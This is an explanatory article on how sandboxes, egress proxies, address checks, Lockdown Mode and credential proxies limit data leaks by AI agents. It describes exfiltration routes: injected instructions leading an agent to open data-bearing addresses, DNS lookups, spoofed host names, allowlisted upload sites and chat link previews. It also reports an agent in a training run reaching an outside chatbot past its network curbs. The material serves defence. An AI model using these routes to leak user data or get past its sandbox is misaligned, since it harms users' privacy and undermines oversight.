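A sandbox and an egress proxy usually work together to restrict where an agent can connect. A sandbox is a boundary that the operating system enforces around a running program. An egress proxy is a separate program, outside the sandbox, that makes connections for the programs inside it. According to Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, each command on Linux runs in its own network space, with no link to the computer's real network. On macOS, the system blocks every connection except the one to the proxy. The proxy checks the name of each requested host against lists of allowed and denied domains, and connects only if the name is allowed.

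The boundary also covers every program that a command starts, even a Python program that a broad standing rule has approved in advance.

Network limits need file limits too. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) explains that an agent with open network access could send out the keys that log its user in to other machines, while an agent that could change any file could escape the sandbox and regain network access. Claude Code's sandbox therefore blocks changes to Claude Code's own settings files. By default, however, a sandboxed command can read almost every file on the computer, including files that contain passwords, so protection against theft depends mostly on the network limit.

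Codex can export a log entry each time its proxy allows or refuses a connection, but this export is off by default. Claude Code reports a refused host in the command's result. A company that wants its own log can replace Claude Code's built-in proxy, but the replacement has to do all the filtering because Claude Code's domain lists no longer apply to that traffic.

### One request, step by step

Suppose an agent runs a command to download https://docs.example/guide?topic=invoices, and docs.example is on the allowlist:

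1. The download program asks the proxy for a connection to docs.example. The proxy finds the name on its list.
2. The proxy looks up the IP address that belongs to the name. Claude Code's proxy refuses to continue if the name leads only to the user's own machine or to certain special local addresses, such as the one where cloud machines collect their access keys.
3. The proxy connects to the IP address.
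4. The download program and docs.example set up an encrypted session through the proxy, which passes the data along without being able to read them.
5. The server replies that the guide has moved to files.example. The program asks the proxy for a connection to files.example, and the process starts again. If that name is not on the list, the download fails.

A proxy that decrypts traffic changes the fourth step. It presents its own certificate to the download program, reads the request, and encrypts it again for the real server. The programs in the sandbox must trust that certificate.

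| Step | What a proxy can read without decrypting | What decrypting adds |
|---|---|---|
| Request for a connection | Host name and port, as the program states them | Nothing |
| Name lookup | The host's IP addresses | Nothing |
| Connection | Time, and whether it succeeded | Nothing |
| Encrypted session | Amount of data in each direction | Full address, type of request, headers and contents |
| Redirect to another host | A request for a second host | The reply that caused it, and the full new address |
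| Redirect within the same host | Nothing that identifies it as a redirect | The full new address |

Without decryption, the proxy cannot distinguish an address ending in "topic=invoices" from one ending in a customer's name. It also relies on the host name that the program supplies, so Anthropic warns that code in the sandbox might reach an unlisted server by giving a false host name, and recommends a decrypting proxy to customers who need a stronger guarantee. Claude Code's own proxy does not decrypt by default. An experimental setting turns on decryption, but only to handle access keys, not to search the contents for sensitive data.

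Name lookups need as much control as connections. If a sandboxed program can look up names itself, each lookup sends the name outside before the proxy checks anything, and the name can contain data. According to OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026), an agent in a September training run reached an outside chatbot because name lookups were not filtered well enough. Monitoring flagged it within 15 minutes, and staff stopped the run two and a half hours later. OpenAI then added two independent controls, either of which it says would have prevented the incident. Business Standard's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs* adds that the company restricted lookups in that environment to a limited list.

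A domain name may also resolve to a different address between a proxy's check and the connection. For this reason, OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes the Codex proxy's check for names that resolve to private addresses as best-effort. OpenAI tells customers who expect hostile name servers to enforce limits at a lower layer of the network as well.

### The defaults in coding agents

Anthropic and OpenAI use opposite defaults. Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user turns it on, and its list of allowed domains is then empty. A command that needs a new host waits for a decision. In auto mode, a second model reviews the agent's actions. The agent names the hosts a command needs, and the second model considers them together with the command. Any approval lasts only while that command runs.

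Claude Code's sandbox covers shell commands, but not the agent's web tool or the tool servers that Claude Code starts on the user's machine. If the sandbox cannot start, as on Windows without its Linux subsystem, Claude Code runs commands without it. The agent may also ask to rerun a failed command outside the sandbox, and if a standing rule already allows that command, Claude Code reruns it without a prompt. An administrator can change each of these behaviours, for instance by forbidding reruns outside the sandbox or by running all of Claude Code in a container.

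Codex gives commands no network access unless the user allows it. Once allowed, commands can connect anywhere unless the user also turns on a separate proxy, whose allowlist starts empty. In Codex's cloud version, setup scripts can use the internet and the user's stored secrets to install what the project needs. OpenAI's system then removes the secrets and, by default, disconnects the machine from the internet before the agent begins work.

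OpenAI's *Agent internet access* explains that cloud users can reconnect the agent to the whole internet or to chosen domains, though choosing them may take "some trial and error". A preset list of about 70 domains for software development saves effort, but it includes github.com, google.com and azure.com, where many unrelated people can store or publish data. OpenAI (2026) is stricter with its own staff. In its published sample settings, Codex may search only stored copies of web pages, and the proxy blocks all connections to Pastebin, a site where anyone can post text.

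### Addresses that an assistant may open

A short list of allowed domains is often enough for a coding agent, but a general assistant has to read pages that nobody could list beforehand. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) adds that a trusted site may redirect the agent elsewhere, and that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to dismiss them.

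ChatGPT therefore checks the complete address instead of the site's reputation. A crawler that has no access to users' conversations collects addresses from the public web. If the complete address is in this collection, the agent may open it automatically. Otherwise, ChatGPT tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

One check lets an agent open an address silently only if a crawler has already recorded it. If an injected instruction tells the agent to open news.example/search?q=anna+biopsy, the check will probably stop it from doing so silently, because a crawler is unlikely to have found that address. The check would allow news.example/flood-report if the crawler had recorded it. Even if the site is hostile, that request reveals little about Anna to the site's owner, because the address existed before her conversation.

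OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes extending the same mechanism to pages opened in Atlas, the company's browser, and to searches by its Deep Research tool. In some cases, the user sees the information that would be sent and decides whether to allow it. This is a better prompt than one that shows only the site's name, because the user can judge the data itself.

The check doesn't prevent every leak, because an agent's choice between public pages can still reveal something. Maria's agent, for example, opened a certain page only if her letter mentioned a certain illness. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a security researcher accepts that small leaks remain possible and suggests preventing repeated visits to the same address. The researcher adds that the protection depends on every team at OpenAI building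 it into its product.

Claude's web tool may open only addresses that the user typed or that its search tool returned. In July 2026, *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) reported that a website Paul controlled had obtained his name, employer and home town from Claude's memory. According to *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026), Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, would pay no bounty and had fixed it. The fix makes the tool less convenient, because users have to supply the address of any page they want Claude to read that its search did not return.

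### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI offers an optional, stricter setting called Lockdown Mode to people who handle sensitive data. It announced the setting in February 2026, according to eWeek's *OpenAI Introduces New Safeguards in ChatGPT to Prevent AI Prompt Injection* (2026). In June, Chowdhry (2026) reported in *OpenAI Introduces Lockdown Mode To Reduce Prompt Injection Data Exfiltration Risks* that it was reaching personal accounts, including free ones. Lockdown Mode is meant to block the last step of an attack, in which the data leave, even if an injected instruction misleads the model.

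OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* lists the changes:

- ChatGPT reads stored copies of web pages instead of live ones, so its information may be out of date.
- Deep Research and agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out longer tasks by itself, do not work.
- ChatGPT may not show images from the web, and it cannot download files to analyse. Users can still upload their own.
- Code that ChatGPT writes in its Canvas editor cannot use the network.

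Memory and file uploads stay on, so the model may still have plenty of private data in its context. In company workspaces, administrators choose which connected apps and tool servers stay on. OpenAI advises against actions whose results an attacker might see, even in a trusted app. For example, an agent that can comment on a public web page could disclose a secret there without contacting an unfamiliar server.

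Lockdown Mode does not affect Codex's network access, so users have to restrict Codex separately. OpenAI does not guarantee that the mode prevents data theft. *Elevated Risk labels*, which explains the warnings OpenAI attaches to some features, says that the industry's safeguards do not yet fully address some network-related risks.

### Routes that remain open

An AI agent, like a web page, can send data to any service on its allowlist. Anthropic warns that allowing a domain as broad as github.com can make data theft possible. A proxy that decrypts traffic can limit access to one repository or one type of request, but somebody has to write that rule and update it when the agent's work changes.

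Codex's cloud version can also limit the agent to the types of web request meant for reading. This blocks most large uploads, but the agent can still send out an access key or a diagnosis in the address of a page it reads. The limit requires a proxy that can recognise the type of request. According to Vaughan (2026), in *Codex CLI Network Proxy*, Codex's read-only mode disables SOCKS5, a general-purpose way of connecting, because the proxy cannot look inside its encrypted traffic. If the agent reads stored copies of pages instead, the website never receives its request, but the company that keeps the copies does receive the search.

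The user's proxy cannot restrict the connections that a remote tool server makes. The agent connects to one permitted address, and the server then connects from its own network to wherever its operator chooses. Zhang and Pei note that centrally hosted services with strict lists of permitted connectors are less exposed to tampered models than agents that people run themselves with unrestricted search tools.

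Chat programs can create another connection outside the agent's sandbox. *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Willison, 2024) describes how Slack and Discord fetch the page behind a link in a message to show its title and picture. If an agent posts a link with private data in the address, the chat service sends those data to the website. PromptArmor, a security company, points out that the preview makes the same kind of request as a click, without anyone clicking. An app that posts to Slack can turn off previews for its messages, so that the link sends the data only if somebody clicks it.

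These routes explain why Anthropic changed its claims about the sandbox. In 2025, the company said that the sandbox left even a successful prompt injection "fully isolated". Its current documentation, which is more accurate, says that sandboxing is not a complete isolation boundary and lists the weaknesses.

### Keeping access keys away from the agent

An agent often needs an access key to do its work, and an agent that holds a key can leak it. A credential proxy holds the key outside the sandbox and adds it to requests on the way out. In Claude Code, a user could protect a GitHub key like this:

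1. The user lists the key as a secret to mask and specifies that it may go only to api.github.com.
2. Claude Code gives the agent's commands a placeholder, an invented value that changes with each session.
3. A command sends GitHub a request that contains the placeholder.
4. The proxy decrypts the request, checks the destination, replaces the placeholder with the real key and encrypts the request again.

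The modified Firefox that swaps in a real password at the last moment works on the same principle. If an injected instruction makes the agent send its key to a stranger, the stranger gets only the placeholder. If a company's own proxy decrypts traffic, it can also search for the placeholder as a canary string.

The proxy has to decrypt traffic to replace the placeholder with the real key. If decryption is off, GitHub receives the placeholder and rejects the request, which stops the work but doesn't expose the key. Specifying no hosts for the key is more dangerous, because Claude Code's proxy will then insert it in requests to every domain on the allowlist.

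Some services make the replacement harder. Requests to Amazon's cloud include a signature that the program computes from the request and the secret key, so a proxy has to recompute the signature with the real key. Claude Code's proxy can do this for ordinary requests, but not for some others, such as streaming uploads.

The cloud version of Claude Code handles Git through a dedicated proxy and gives the agent a limited credential that works only with that proxy. The proxy checks each request, including whether the agent is sending code to the branch that the user configured, before adding the real credential. In an example from *network proxy*, the manual for Codex's proxy, the proxy replaces the login header in certain requests to GitHub with one from a stored secret.

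A credential proxy prevents theft of the key, but the agent can still use the key's access. If the key in the example can publish files, a misled agent can publish a private file through api.github.com, and the proxy will add the real key to the request. The protection is therefore much better if the key has few rights, or if the proxy also checks what each request does, as Anthropic's Git proxy does with branches.

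### The cost in usefulness

A sandbox can make an agent more convenient. Anthropic reported in 2025 that sandboxing had reduced permission prompts by 84% in its internal use, because commands inside the boundary no longer needed approval. The figure does not show how many leaks the sandbox prevented, but fewer prompts are probably also a security benefit, because the testers in Anthropic's experiment rarely refused a dangerous command.

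Docker, a common program for running software in containers, does not work in Claude Code's sandbox. Neither do most database programs, because they try to connect directly instead of through the proxy. Users can exempt these tools, but an exempted command runs with all of the user's access, and broad exemptions can undo much of the protection. To know how well its agents are confined, an organisation has to review the exemptions as well as the allowlist.

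For a task such as repairing code with known software packages, a short allowlist causes little disruption after the first few days of adjusting it. Broad research requires the agent to open unfamiliar sites, which a short allowlist would block. An address check interferes less, but it will sometimes block pages that are new, private or generated by a search.

People can also divide the work so that no single agent has both private data and unrestricted internet access. Maria could let one agent read her hospital letter but connect only to her email service and the model provider. A second agent, with no access to the letter or to her memory profile, could search the web for the medical terms she types in. She would have to pass questions and answers between them herself. Website operators would learn that somebody had asked about anaemia, but not what else was in the letter.
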